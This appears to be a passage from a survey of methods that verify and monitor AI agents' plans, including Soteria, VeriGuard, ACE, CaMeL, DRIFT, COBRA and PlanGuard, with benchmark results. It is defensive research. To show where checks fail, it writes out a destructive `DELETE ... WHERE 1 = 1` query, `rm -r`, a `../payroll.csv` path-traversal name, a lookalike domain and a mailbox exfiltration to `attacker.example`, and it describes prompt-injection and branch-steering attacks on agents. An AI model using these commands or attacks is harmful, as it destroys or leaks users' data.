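Writing the rules took a few hours for each benchmark, mostly spent reading the policy and checking the model's output. It produced 24 formulas for the airline, 33 for the shop and 41 for Toolathlon. This is little work, since a company can reuse the formulas for every later request. A company's own staff would probably need longer, though, because the people who did this work had also designed the rule language.

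The clause-by-clause check covered only rules that are about changes to stored data and that a checker can enforce from the log of tool calls. It would exclude a rule that the customer must agree to a change before the agent makes it, because customers agree in conversation, not through a tool. None of the 57 customer-service formulas requires such agreement.

He and colleagues print all 98 formulas next to the rules they stand for, so readers can compare the two. Several formulas are weaker than the words beside them:

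| Rule in words | What the printed formula requires | What it would accept |
|---|---|---|
| Compensation is $100 per passenger for a cancelled flight and $50 for a delayed one | Either amount; a separate formula requires a flight that was cancelled or delayed | $100 per passenger for a delay |
| A changed booking keeps its origin and destination | A change of cabin class, or an earlier search on the booking's route | A search on the old route, then new flights to another city |
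| An order must belong to the authenticated customer | An earlier lookup of any customer who has that order | An authenticated customer cancelling somebody else's order |
| Database deletions must include a WHERE clause | The word "WHERE" somewhere in the query | `DELETE FROM orders WHERE 1 = 1`, which deletes every order |

The printed list abbreviates some conditions, so the software may be stricter. If it isn't, some of the shop's payment rules have no effect. They require the payment method for a return or exchange to come from the customer's profile or the order. But the order condition checks only that the agent has looked up the order, which other rules already require, so any payment method passes.

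Formulas that search for words can also be too strict and too lax at once. One Toolathlon rule forbids terminal commands that contain both "rm", the command for deleting files, and a file extension such as ".csv". It would block the harmless `python format.py sales.csv`, because "format" contains "rm". But `rm -r reports`, which deletes a folder of spreadsheets, passes both that rule and a second one against destructive deletions.

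Toolathlon's email rules, for example, don't limit who can receive an email. They require an email to have a subject, a body and an "@" in the recipient's address, and they require the agent to read a message before deleting it. The plan that sends Michelle's mailbox to `backup@attacker.example` would satisfy all of these rules if it included a subject line. This did no harm in the experiments because Toolathlon's tasks contain no attackers, but a company that copied the rules would need to add one that limits recipients.

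While auditing their results, He and colleagues corrected or added some rules, which shows that the review by hand had missed some mistakes. Auditing is a sensible way to improve rules, but Soteria's 100% conformance is therefore to rules that the researchers had adjusted after seeing results on the same tasks. It does not measure how well a first set of rules would protect a company that had no such results to audit.

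The changes could also have widened the gap between Soteria and its competitors. Suppose an audit finds a harmful action by an unguarded agent, and the researchers add a rule against it. The unguarded agent's conformance falls, and so does its success rate, because rule-breaking runs don't count as successes. Soteria's monitor enforces the new rule, so its conformance stays at 100%. Loosening a rule would have had the opposite effect. He and colleagues don't report how many rules they changed or in which direction, so readers can't tell how much the changes affected the gap. A fairer test would finalize the rules first and then use new tasks, with people judging the runs against the written policy.

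### VeriGuard: proving the policy code

Soteria's rules are formulas that people have checked. *VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) describes a Google system that has a model write the policy as a Python program and then tries to prove the program correct. VeriGuard uses this program as a run-time monitor and doesn't check plans.

The work before deployment starts with a request in plain English, such as a ban on emailing people outside the company, and a description of the agent. From these, a model drafts a policy function, which takes facts about a proposed action and decides whether to allow it. With a separate prompt, a model also drafts the function's specification, a list of preconditions and postconditions. VeriGuard then refines both drafts:

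1. A model looks for ambiguities in the drafts and puts questions to the user. If no user is available, a model picks the most plausible answers itself.
2. A model writes test cases, and VeriGuard revises the function until it passes them or reaches a limit on attempts.
3. Nagini, a verifier for Python programs, tries to prove that the function satisfies its specification. If the proof fails, VeriGuard uses the error to revise the drafts and tries again, up to a limit.

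Once the agent is running, VeriGuard intercepts each action, extracts the facts the function needs and calls the function. If the function rejects the action, VeriGuard can end the task, block the whole action, stop only the offending tool call, or report the broken policy to the agent and request a new plan.

Miculicich and colleagues tested VeriGuard on Agent Security Bench, which attacks agents through the user's prompt, tool outputs, poisoned memories and hidden triggers. They compared it with a simple guardrail that gives a model the same information and asks whether the action complies. Both defences reduced successful attacks to 0% with every model, so the differences lie in how many tasks the agents still completed:

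| Model | Attacks that succeeded, no defence | Tasks completed, simple guardrail | Tasks completed, VeriGuard |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 51.9% | 40.2% | 63.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 52.1% | 51.5% | 67.3% |
| GPT-4.1 | 63.7% | 44.6% | 57.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 49.9% | 68.3% | 85.1% |

Much of VeriGuard's advantage may come from how it responds to a violation. With Gemini 2.5 Flash, agents completed 44.6% of tasks when VeriGuard only stopped the offending tool calls, close to the simple guardrail's 40.2%. They completed 63.3% when it also asked for a new plan. When it only asked for a new plan, without stopping any tool calls, it let 11.9% of attacks through.

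The proof also made no measurable difference to security. When the researchers added VeriGuard's components one at a time, the first draft of the policy cut the attack success rate from 53.5% to about 10%, and later refinements brought it to 0% before Nagini was used to prove anything. The benchmark's attacks were too easy to show what the proof adds. A proof could still matter for rare inputs that are in neither the tests nor the benchmark.

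The other two benchmarks measure access control. EICU-AC tests whether a system can tell if a hospital user may see the data needed to answer a question, and VeriGuard decided every case correctly with all three models tested. On Mind2Web-SC, which restricts what certain users may do on websites, its accuracy was 95.1% to 97.2%, below the 98.4% of a competing system, AGrail. Miculicich and colleagues' figures show that VeriGuard missed 1% of the violations on Mind2Web-SC with two of the three models, although they write that it blocks every violation on both benchmarks.

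### When a model writes both the policy and its specification

If one model writes the function and the specification from the same request, it can put the same misunderstanding into both. Suppose Michelle's company allows email only to its own addresses, which end in `@valleysharks.com`, and the model writes:

```
def allowed(address):
    return address.endswith("valleysharks.com")

specification:  allowed(address) is true exactly when
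                address ends with "valleysharks.com"
```

The function satisfies its specification, so the proof succeeds. But an attacker can register the domain `evilvalleysharks.com` and receive Michelle's mail. The model's own tests would probably include a colleague's address and a stranger's Gmail address, and the function would handle both correctly.

The proof therefore establishes that two texts written by the same model agree. This is somewhat useful because a careless mistake, unlike a misunderstanding, is unlikely to appear in both drafts. A specification can also be shorter than the code and so easier for a person to check. In the example, however, the specification merely restates the code, and a reader who overlooked the missing "@" in one would probably overlook it in the other. Miculicich and colleagues accept that the guarantee depends on a user confirming that the specification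 reflects the intention. That confirmation is missing when VeriGuard answers its own questions because no user is available.

Another model has to extract the proved function's arguments from the agent's text. VeriGuard's prompt illustrates this step with a request to email `alex@example.com` and a person called Dona Jhonson. The model is supposed to return two addresses, but the second, `dona@example.com`, appears nowhere in the request. The policy function would then check the guessed address, while the agent might send the email to a different one. A checker that reads the recipient directly from the tool call avoids this problem.

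### How accurately models translate rules

Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, reviewed 38 studies of how to specify, verify and enforce safe behaviour in agents, and concluded that specification is the bottleneck. Models rarely have trouble with the grammar of a formal language. More than 90% of their formulas in temporal logic, which expresses the order of events, are well formed. Whether a formula has the intended meaning is another matter:

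| What the model had to write | Method | Correct in meaning |
|---|---|---|
| A planning problem in PDDL, a language for automated planners | GPT-4o, without examples | 24.8% |
| The same | The best specially trained model | 34.2% |
| A formula in temporal logic | Translation without help | 44.4% |
| The same | A person resolves ambiguities | 86.11% |

Of the planning problems GPT-4o wrote, 96.1% were well formed, but almost three quarters of the total were valid PDDL that described the wrong problem. A checker that tests only whether the PDDL is well formed would have accepted them.

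These figures are weak evidence of how a model of late 2026 would perform. GPT-4o dates from May 2024, and the temporal-logic results come from a paper published in 2023. Describing a planning problem's starting situation and goal is also a different task from stating what an agent must never do. The temporal-logic paper didn't concern agents, and three of the survey's authors who screened it again all judged it outside the survey's scope. Dantas and colleagues give the planning figures their lowest certainty rating, meaning that further studies would probably produce substantially different numbers. The evidence that there is a gap between form and meaning is stronger than the evidence for its size, and current models may have narrowed it considerably.

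The improvement from 44.4% to 86.11% suggests that much of the difficulty comes from ambiguity in the request. "Refunds above $500 need approval" doesn't specify whether two refunds for one order count together, and even a better model can't determine which the shop intends from that sentence. The system can prompt the user for clarification, as VeriGuard does. Dantas and colleagues also suggest having a model translate the rule into a formula twice and searching for a case that satisfies only one of the translations. For the refund rule, the search might produce two $400 refunds for the same order, and the shop could decide whether to allow them without reading a formula.

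A related approach lets people read the formal statement itself. One experimental verifier does this for Ansible, a language for administering computer systems. It translates the user's request into a formal language that resembles English, the user confirms that the translation matches what they meant, and the verifier checks the generated code against it. On 21 code-generation tasks, it verified correct code in 83% of cases and identified incorrect code in 92%. The statements stay readable because a separate knowledge base supplies the technical details of particular systems, so the knowledge base must also be correct.

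### Rules that resist formalisation

Some rules are hard to formalise even when everybody agrees on what they mean, sometimes because the log of calls lacks the necessary facts. A formula can require the agent to identify a customer before opening an account, but the log doesn't show whether the customer number is genuine or whether the person typing it is that customer. Dantas and colleagues compared seven systems and found that six did not address such credentials and the seventh did so only in part. They propose checking each identifier against a list of valid ones, which would stop an agent from inventing a number but not a customer from using somebody else's.

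Rules about purpose have a similar problem. A hospital may want its agent to open a patient's record only for that patient's care, but the call is the same whether a doctor is treating the patient or looking up a neighbour. A developer can approximate the rule, for instance by requiring an appointment that day, but this will block some legitimate uses and allow some improper ones.

Other rules limit how often something happens. A company may accept a model misreading one invoice in a thousand but not one in ten. A formula that is either true or false of each run can't express this limit, and measuring the error rate takes many runs. Only one system in the survey, ProbGuard, works with probabilities. It learns from past runs how likely an agent is to reach an unsafe state, so it needs a record of similar work.

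Rules that cover several agents together are harder still to write. Suppose one agent may read salaries but not send email, and another may send email but not read salaries. The first can pass the salaries to the second, which then emails them, without either agent breaking its own rules. Preventing this requires a rule about both agents and a record of what passes between them. According to Dantas and colleagues, the two studies in their survey that verify several agents at once treat them as a single process, which leaves out much of what can go wrong between them.

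In a new field, there may also be no correct formal version to compare a translation with. Researchers can measure accuracy on benchmarks because somebody has already written the correct formulas. A company that formalises its own policy for the first time has only the policy.

### What incomplete rules still prevent

Checking is still useful despite these limits, because a rule can exclude a specific harm without describing everything the agent should do. If written correctly, Meijer's rule about Michelle's mailbox stops a plan from putting her mail into a message to an outsider, even if the company has no other rules. Adding prohibitions later can only narrow what plans may do, so a company can start by prohibiting the few actions it fears most.

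A misstated rule may also prevent most of the harm. The airline's compensation formula, as printed, lets an agent pay a delayed passenger twice the proper amount, but it still rules out a $5,000 voucher. Agents do break simple rules. In He and colleagues' experiments, GPT-5.4-mini committed 29 violations in 50 airline tasks when it had only the written policy.

The effect of an omission depends on what the system does by default. Soteria's monitor allows any call that no rule or precondition forbids, so a forgotten rule leaves an action open. In TACIT, code can't open a file without a capability, so a forgotten permission leads to a refused request. Users notice refusals and complain, but a missing prohibition may go unnoticed until somebody misuses the action. Listing what is allowed is therefore safer for actions that can't be undone.

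The argument for incomplete rules fails if people treat a passed check as proof that a plan is safe in general. If a company stops asking users to approve payments because a checker verifies every plan, it loses a protection against all the harms its rules leave out. Dantas and colleagues call this false assurance, and recommend treating rules like code, with version control, tests and peer review. A useful test is to write plans that should fail, such as the one with two $400 refunds, and see whether the checker rejects them.

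## Running a verified plan

A proof that a plan obeys a rule applies to the plan's text. It also applies to the run if the executor follows the plan, the tools behave as their contracts describe, and the facts the plan checks stay true until the steps that rely on them have run.

### Interpreters and guided language models

ACE and Meijer's workflows use an interpreter to run the checked program step by step. The interpreter can depart from the plan only through a bug. Dongol's theorems explicitly assume a trusted interpreter, so that the language model can't skip or alter the plan's steps.

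An interpreter also follows a plan that no longer makes sense, as in the ACE run that failed because the adapter code looked for a file's size in the wrong place.

Soteria normally gives the plan to a language model as guidance, and the model still chooses every tool call. The model gets a flowchart of the remaining steps, which Soteria shortens as results arrive. For example, if a booking turns out to be 26 hours old, Soteria removes the branch for bookings made within the last 24 hours.

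This freedom is useful when a request contains something that the plan leaves out. In an example from He and colleagues, a customer wants to cancel reservation RES123 and also asks about RES456. The plan covers only the cancellation, but the model can look up the second reservation anyway. However, it can also cancel RES123 without checking whether the customer has already flown, even if the plan includes that check.

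### How much verification changed the agent's behaviour

He and colleagues measured what each part of Soteria contributes on the 50 airline tasks. They started with unverified plans and added one component at a time. In the table, "no violation" is the share of tasks in which the agent broke no rule, and "success" is the share that it also completed:

| Configuration | GPT-5.4-mini, no violation | GPT-5.4-mini, success | Gemini 3 Flash, no violation | Gemini 3 Flash, success |
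|---|---|---|---|---|
| Unverified plan | 74% | 44% | 54% | 32% |
| With verification | 80% | 46% | 56% | 32% |
| With sub-plans as well | 80% | 50% | 58% | 38% |
| With the run-time monitor as well | 100% | 60% | 100% | 62% |

Verification kept three more tasks free of violations with GPT-5.4-mini and one more with Gemini. Gains this small could be due to chance, because the share of tasks without violations had a standard deviation of 5.2 percentage points across five runs of GPT-5.4-mini on the same tasks without safeguards.

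When no plan passed verification, Soteria used the best one it had. But the bigger problem was probably the model that carried out the plans, because it could still make calls that a verified plan didn't contain. Sub-plans let GPT-5.4-mini produce far more plans that passed verification, yet it broke rules in a fifth of the tasks with or without sub-plans. If unverified plans had caused most of the violations, sub-plans should have prevented many of them.

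The monitor raised both models to 100% compliance because it enforces the same rules that the researchers used for scoring. More surprisingly, blocking calls did not reduce the number of tasks completed. Gemini completed 62% of the tasks both with and without the monitor, if violations are ignored. Its success rate, which counts only tasks completed without violations, rose from 38% to 62%.

The results show that verification is a weak safeguard when a model can deviate from the plan. The experiment did not test the monitor with unverified plans, so it does not show how much verification helps once a monitor is in place.

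### The monitor's checks

Before each call, Soteria's monitor checks the tool's precondition against the actual arguments. It then adds the proposed call to its log of earlier calls, with the result left blank, and tests whether the extended log breaks a rule. If the model tries to cancel too early, the check looks like this:

```
log so far:      Get-Resv("RES123")              → reservation details
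proposed call:   Cancel-Resv("RES123", "other")  → ?
rule φ1 needs:   an earlier No-Flown("RES123") that returned true
found:           none
decision:        block the call
```

The monitor has a finite list of calls with known values, so it can test a rule about "every call" by going through the list, without a prover. It also keeps an index of which rules mention which tools, and tests only the relevant rules.

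The checks took very little time. With GPT-5.4-mini on the airline tasks, the median step took about one second with the monitor and two and a half seconds without it. He et al. attribute the saving to the monitor's stopping mistakes early that the agent would otherwise have had to repair.

After a call, the monitor records the result. Soteria aborts the run if the result contradicts the tool's postcondition, because the proof relied on it. The monitor also tests any rules that depend on the result. These tests can detect a violation but not prevent it, because the tool has already acted. At the end of the task, the monitor tests rules that require a later call, such as reading back every file the agent wrote.

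### Recovery from a blocked call

When the monitor blocks the early cancellation, it sends the model the rule that the call would have broken and a suggestion to call `No-Flown` first. The model calls `No-Flown`, gets `true`, and retries the cancellation. The monitor now allows the call because the log contains the required check.

If `No-Flown` returns `false`, retrying the cancellation won't help. The model can use the flowchart to find another branch, such as the one that ends by telling the customer the airline doesn't permit the cancellation. If the plan has no suitable branch, the model has to work out what to do from the plan and the reason for the block.

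The main advantage of keeping a plan alongside a monitor is that the plan contains a sequence of calls meant to complete the task. With only a monitor, an agent learns that a call is forbidden, but not which permitted calls would complete the task. If the plan is fully verified, the whole sequence obeys the rules.

### Strict mode

In Soteria's strict mode, the model may call only the tools that the plan allows in its current state. If it tries to cancel when the next step is `No-Flown`, Soteria rejects the call and lists the available tools. Once the plan has finished, Soteria silently drops any further calls. The lookup of RES456 would fail in this mode because it isn't in the plan, even though it is harmless and the customer asked for it.

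In strict mode, Soteria accepts only fully verified plans and doesn't use the run-time monitor, so the guarantee depends on how closely it compares each call with the plan. He and colleagues are clear about how it compares tools but less clear about arguments. Every refusal in their example happens because the model names a tool that isn't available in the current state. If Soteria compared only tool names, the model could check RES123 and then cancel RES456, and nothing would test the cancellation against φ1. To prevent this, the executor has to take the arguments from the plan's variables, as an interpreter would.

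The experiments used guided mode, so they don't show how many tasks an agent would fail to complete in strict mode.

### ACE's isolated workers

ACE's interpreter can't depart from the plan in this way, so Li and colleagues focus on what the plan's code and the tools could do outside it. They divide the executor into separate processes. A privileged orchestrator process starts the others and passes messages between them. One worker process runs the plan, and each tool has its own worker. Every worker runs in a container, an isolated environment with its own permissions.

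When the plan worker reaches the call to `DocumentLoader` in the plan that loads and summarizes `file.txt`, it sends a request to the orchestrator and waits. The orchestrator checks the arguments against the tool's schema and starts a container that has access to files. The loader returns the text to the orchestrator, which checks that it is a string before passing it to the plan worker. The summarizer then gets the text in another container, which can't access files unless the summarizer needs to.

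The plan worker has no access to files either, and it can't start tools itself. Li and colleagues worry less about attacks here than accidents, because the planner has read only the user's request. For example, the container would stop a badly written plan from overwriting a system file.

ACE's flow analysis follows only the data that the plan passes from one tool to another, so the containers also have to stop tools from exchanging data in other ways. If all the tools shared a folder, a tool that loads bank details could leave a copy there for the email tool to read, and that flow would not appear in the plan the checker approved. The separate containers share no files, and the workers can't send messages to each other directly.

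Two tools with network access could still exchange data through a server outside the user's computer, where ACE's file restrictions don't apply. Li and colleagues also exclude attacks in which a tool breaks out of its container or learns about other processes indirectly, for instance from their timing.

The orchestrator's type checks catch malformed results but not false ones. If a malicious ride-hailing tool returns the wrong fare, the fare passes the check because it is still a number. If the tool returns an instruction instead, the check rejects it when the plan expects a number but accepts it when the plan expects a string. ACE protects against an accepted instruction by keeping the string away from the planner.

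### A refund whose amount is unknown in advance

A checker can prove something about a value that nobody knows yet, but only the run can supply the value. Consider a plan for the shop from the previous section, which wants a manager to approve refunds above $500:

```
order = get_order(id="A17")
if order.total > 500:
    ok = ask_manager(order="A17", amount=order.total)
    if not ok:
        return "refused"
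refund(order="A17", amount=order.total, card=order.card)
```

The checker doesn't need to know the total to prove that every refund above $500 has the manager's approval, that the amount comes from the order, and that the money goes back to the original card. The proof relies on the contracts of the three tools. According to the contract of `get_order`, the total is a number, is not negative and is what the customer paid. The executor can test part of this when the result arrives:

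| `order.total` | What the executor does |
|---|---|
| `80` | Refunds $80 without asking the manager |
| `800` | Asks the manager, and refunds $800 if the answer is `true` |
| `"80 dollars"` | Stops, because the result is not a number |
| `-80` | Stops, because the contract excludes negative totals |
| `480`, although the customer paid $80 | Refunds $480 without asking the manager |

In the last case, the plan runs as verified and the shop still loses $400. The executor can't check whether the total matches what the customer paid, because `get_order` is its only source for the amount paid. To catch the error, the shop would need a second source, such as the card company's record of the payment.

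### Other checks that wait for the run

File paths and web addresses often depend on results too. Suppose a plan saves an email attachment in the folder `invoices` under the name the sender chose. If the sender named it `../payroll.csv`, the file would end up outside the folder, because `..` refers to the folder above. The plan contains only a variable in place of the name, so the library has to check the complete path when the plan tries to write the file. TACIT's library checks file paths and web hosts during the run.

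Resource use is hard to predict as well, because it depends on the size of the data and the speed of the tools. ACE's orchestrator can set a time limit for each tool's worker. If a tool exceeds the limit, the orchestrator stops it and reports the failure to the plan worker.

Failures of this kind can also undermine a proof, because Soteria proves rules only for runs that reach one of the plan's final states. Stopping early can't break a prohibition, but it can break a rule that requires a later step. For example, a rule might require the agent to read back a file after writing it, and every complete path through the plan might include that step. If the next tool after the write fails permanently, the agent never reads the file back.

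Retrying a failed call can also repeat an action that already succeeded. If a call fails during the run, for example from a network timeout, Soteria reports the error to the model, which tries again from the same state. Repeating a lookup is fine, but a refund may have gone through before the connection failed, and a second attempt would then pay the customer twice. The payment tool can prevent this if each refund has a unique number and the tool ignores numbers it has already processed.

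TACIT also has to contain exceptions, which can reveal secrets, while the plan runs. Its method also covers early returns and breaks out of loops, which, as Odersky and colleagues explain, Scala implements as exceptions. The compiler adds one static check, which prevents an exception from carrying a capability out with it.

### Changes between check and use

Suppose the manager takes an hour to approve the $800 refund for order A17. Meanwhile, the customer phones the shop, and an employee refunds the order by hand. When the approval arrives, the plan refunds the order again.

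The proof didn't allow for this. No step between the lookup and the refund changes the customer's order, so the checker treated the facts established by the lookup as still true. Frame conditions don't help because they cover only the tools, not what other people and programs do at the same time.

Soteria's rule about flown reservations has a similar gap. It requires an earlier check that no flight has been flown, but sets no limit on how old that check can be. A customer could start a chat before boarding and confirm the cancellation after landing. Both the static proof and the run-time monitor would accept the cancellation, since the log contains a check of the right reservation with the right result.

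Data can change between an agent's check and the action that relies on it, which security researchers call a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw. Lilienthal and Hong built a benchmark of 66 user tasks to study this flaw in agents (*Mind the Gap*, 2025). They tried rewriting prompts, monitoring whether the relevant data had changed, and fusing tools so that the check and the action happen in one call. With all three together, the share of runs with such a flaw fell only from 12% to 8%.

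The gap between choosing an action and carrying it out can be very short. *Atomicity for Agents* (2026) examines agents that operate a web browser. The page may change after the agent chooses a button but before it clicks, so the click does something else. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026) summarizes research that found this problem to be common and exploitable in ten open-source browser agents. The review lists only two papers on such flaws, so there is little evidence about how often they cause harm in practice.

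An interpreter shortens some gaps because it doesn't wait for a model to decide on each step, but it can't shorten the hour spent waiting for the manager. Looking up the order again just before the refund would help, but an employee could still act between the second lookup and the payment. The payment service can close the gap by checking that the order still has money to refund and paying it out as one indivisible operation. The checker then relies on the payment service to do this.

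### The trusted base

The guarantee depends on several pieces of software besides the plan, and a fault in any of them can defeat it:

| Component | What a fault can do |
|---|---|
| Checker or prover | Accept a plan that breaks the rule |
| Compiler or translator | Produce a program that differs from the one the checker approved |
| Interpreter | Carry out a step wrongly, or let the plan's code do things that the language forbids |
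| Tool wrapper, the code that connects a plan's function to a real service | Make a permitted call do something that its contract excludes |
| Isolation | Let data reach a tool by a route outside the plan |

The danger from a fault in the checker depends on who controls the planner. A planner that has read only the user's request will rarely write an unusual program that the checker wrongly accepts, but an attacker who controls the planner can search for such a program and submit it. ACE relies on the planner being honest, so it can tolerate more of these faults than TACIT, which assumes that the planner may be hostile.

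An interpreter has to enforce the limits of the plan language even when a program is written to get around them. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-5120* (2025), a public vulnerability notice, reports that attackers could escape the restricted Python interpreter in one version of Hugging Face's smolagents library despite its static and dynamic checks. ACE's container offers some protection against a similar fault, because code that escaped the interpreter would still have no access to the user's files, and an attacker would need a second fault to reach them.

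Faults in tool wrappers are harder to contain, because a tool needs real permissions to do its job. The wrapper for `refund` must have access to the payment service, so a container won't stop it from reading an amount in dollars as cents, or from sending the money to the customer's newest card instead of the one in the call. TACIT similarly relies on its local model not to keep one user's confidential text and use it in a later answer. The type system can ensure that the model gets no capabilities, but it can't prevent the model from retaining text.

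Soteria's run-time monitor works without Dafny and Z3, so if they accepted a bad plan, the monitor would still block a call that broke a rule. But the static check and the monitor use the same rules and contracts, so the monitor can't make up for a mistake in those.

Users can also check a monitor's policy before relying on it. *Tether* (2026) describes a monitor whose policy depends on earlier events in the run. The user names a state that should never occur, such as secret data in the agent's context. A language model then tries either to write a proof in Lean that the policy never allows that state or to find a sequence of actions that leads to it. Lean checks the proof, which uses induction on the length of the run to show that no permitted action leads from an acceptable state to the forbidden one. But the proof assumes that the monitor recognizes secret data when it arrives.

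## Tasks that cannot be planned in advance, and attacks that leave the plan unchanged

A planner that writes the whole plan before any tool runs can only prepare for situations it can predict. Hostile text that arrives later cannot change the plan, but neither can useful text, such as a notice that the user must log in first. How much this limits the agent depends on the task.

### Three kinds of task

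Some tasks have fixed steps. For the AgentDojo request "Pay the bill in bill-december-2023.txt", the agent reads the file and sends the money. The planner doesn't know the amount or the payee, but it can use a variable for each.

Other tasks have branches that a planner can foresee. The shopkeeper's plan emails the buyer only if fewer than ten items are left, and the airline's plan cancels only if no flight has been flown. The planner can specify these conditions and write a branch for each possible result before the results are available.

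In the third kind of task, the next steps appear only in the content the agent reads. If the user says "do what this email asks", the planner can't determine in advance whether the agent will need to book a room, translate a document or delete a folder. It could write a branch for every tool, but then the email's author could choose almost any action.

*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) uses a related classification that shows why the third kind is also the most dangerous. It separates requests that state the action and all its details, requests that state the action but leave details such as the payee to a file, and requests that leave the action itself to the content the agent reads. An example of the last is a request to do everything on an online to-do list, where an injected instruction looks like one more item. With GPT-4o-mini and no defence, standard injections succeeded in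 87.5% of cases when the request left the action open, and in 63.9% and 43.3% for the other two kinds.

### The cost of a fixed plan

Many results on agent security come from AgentDojo, which hardly measures this loss. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen et al., 2026) reports that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require an agent to change its plan along the way, compared with all 60 tasks in its own benchmark. These tasks involve online shopping, GitHub and everyday errands, and take 7.1 steps on average, about twice as many as AgentDojo's. Each contains at least one genuine instruction from a third party, such as a checkout page's request to log in, so an agent that ignores every instruction outside the user's request will fail.

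The table shows the share of tasks that agents completed without an attack. CaMeL runs a program written in advance, while DRIFT, by some of the same researchers, lets the agent depart from its plan under certain conditions:

| Model | No defence | CaMeL | DRIFT |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 53.3% | 0% | 30.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 51.7% | 0% | 36.7% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 60.0% | 0% | 33.3% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10.0% | 0% | 11.7% |

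No attack succeeded against CaMeL either, but it completed none of the users' tasks.

Li and colleagues wanted tasks that an agent can't plan in advance, which partly explains the zeros. The results therefore don't show how often real users ask for such tasks. The zeros may also exaggerate the limits of planning ahead, because a planner could foresee a login page and write a branch for it. CaMeL's planner may not have been prompted to expect so many surprises.

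An experiment in *DRIFT* (Li, Liu and colleagues, 2025) comes closer to answering Meijer's question about what is lost by planning in advance. GPT-4o-mini completed 63.6% of AgentDojo tasks without restrictions, but only 43.2% with a list of tool calls and arguments fixed in advance. Success fell little on tasks of one or two steps but sharply on tasks of three or more. The agent still chose its own calls within these limits, so this isn't quite the same as running a finished program.

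The loss of 20 percentage points is much larger than the 6% of AgentDojo's tasks that need replanning. Most of it therefore probably came from mistakes in the initial list, which an unrestricted agent could have corrected while working. GPT-4o-mini is a small model from 2024, and a better planner should lose less to such mistakes, but it would not help with a task whose steps are in an unread email.

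### Plans for a screen the planner can't see

Some agents operate a computer by looking at the screen, clicking and typing. They normally look again after every action, so each page they visit can influence the next step. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) replaces this loop with a single plan that the planner writes without seeing the screen.

Their method, NOVA, has the planner check each assumption before acting on it. Simplified and with other names, part of a plan might be:

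```
screen = describe_screen()
if verify_hypothesis(screen, "a cookie notice is visible"):
    click(find("button that rejects cookies"))
    screen = describe_screen()
if verify_hypothesis(screen, "the search page is open"):
    type_text(find("search box"), "train times")
```

A quarantined model describes the screen and locates the buttons. Another compares the description with the planner's prediction and returns true or false. The interpreter takes the matching branch, and the planner never receives these results. The planner's prompt also includes standard routines for problems that occur on most websites, such as cookie notices and failed clicks.

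This makes the plans much longer:

| Average per plan | AgentDojo | Screen tasks, basic prompt | Screen tasks, NOVA |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 52 | 72 | 213 |
| Tool calls | 4.9 | 19.8 | 41.1 |
| Branches | 3.7 | 11.3 | 39.7 |

About half the steps in a plan are fallbacks that don't run. The plans are also too long for most users to review, so an approval prompt would offer little protection.

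On OSWorld, a benchmark of ordinary computer tasks, agents with NOVA retained up to 57% of the performance of leading models that look at the screen as they work. Smaller open models improved by up to 19%. Foerster and colleagues counted a task as solved if at least one of several independent attempts succeeded, so these figures are upper limits. A real user would have to work out which attempt had succeeded, and the failed attempts might already have changed files. Still, the results show that planners can foresee far more of a task than the zero scores on AgentDyn suggest.

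### Attacks inside a permitted plan

Variables and branches let content affect a run without changing the plan. An attacker can use this to put false data into a permitted argument. For example, the invoice that SPA's labels caught contained the attacker's account number.

A flow rule that stops payment of a false bill also blocks genuine bills from the same source. A contract can limit payments to saved payees and set a maximum amount, but it can't detect a false bill from a known supplier if the amount is within the limit.

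Content can also lead the agent to take a branch that the plan permits but the user wouldn't want. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. In their example, an advertisement looks like a cookie notice, so the agent clicks it and lands on the attacker's website. The plan already included a click to handle cookie notices.

A flow rule can treat everything in a branch as dependent on the branch's condition, as ACE does for secrecy. With trust labels, a checker could then reject any important action that depends on an untrusted condition. But this would also reject many useful plans, because branches are often meant to respond to what a website or an email contains. A contract can instead limit what each branch may do, whichever one runs.

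The third possibility is a misleading summary or answer, like the one that passed on a planted hotel recommendation in TACIT's tests. Flow rules can keep that answer away from a booking tool, but they can't stop the user from believing it. A contract also can't express whether a summary is true and complete. Dongol's theorems don't cover misleading answers because they concern only leaks.

| Attack | What a flow rule can do | What a contract can do |
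|---|---|---|
| False data in a permitted argument | Block data from untrusted sources, including honest data | Limit the permitted values |
| Content that selects a branch | Block important actions that depend on untrusted conditions | Limit the actions in each branch |
| Misleading summary | Keep the summary away from protected tools | Check its form, but not whether it is true |

Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026) tested limits on individual branches in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*. In their system, COBRA, the planner writes a branching plan and states which websites, tools and values each branch may use, before the agent reads anything untrusted. If the task needs an important value that neither the user nor an authorised source supplies, COBRA asks the user for it while planning.

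COBRA checks web requests and tool calls instead of clicks, because the same click can open a tab or confirm a bank transfer. If the user has approved a description of a website's operations, COBRA can allow one operation and block another. Otherwise it can only limit which websites the agent contacts. It doesn't control actions that stay on the user's computer, such as deleting a local file.

Zingrillo and colleagues built a benchmark of 101 tasks with 199 attack cases. In the 74 cases that other agents could also run, attacks succeeded 94.4% of the time against an ordinary agent and 89.5% against an agent with an isolated planner. None of the 199 attacks succeeded against COBRA, which retained 97% of the usefulness of the agent with the isolated planner and raised four false alarms in 138 harmless runs.

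The benchmark counts an attack as successful when a harmful action violates the limits in force at that point. COBRA is designed to block such actions, so its score of zero mainly confirms that it enforces its own limits. An attacker can still choose between two branches if both stay within their limits. Nine attacks were meant to add an action that the plan didn't contain. An isolated planner should prevent this, yet the attacks succeeded 89% of the time against the agent that had one, which is hard to explain. Perhaps the benchmark counted a planned click with an unplanned effect as a new action.

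### Comparing an adaptive agent with a plan

Another way to regain flexibility is to let the agent choose each step after reading the results, and use a plan only to judge its choices. Gong and Deng (2026), in *PlanGuard*, have an isolated planner read the user's request and the tools' definitions and list the calls it expects, with their arguments. The agent doesn't have to follow this list. PlanGuard compares each proposed call with the list:

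1. If the tool and arguments match an expected call exactly, PlanGuard allows the call.
2. If the tool isn't on the list, it blocks the call.
3. If only the arguments differ, a language model decides whether the difference is harmless.

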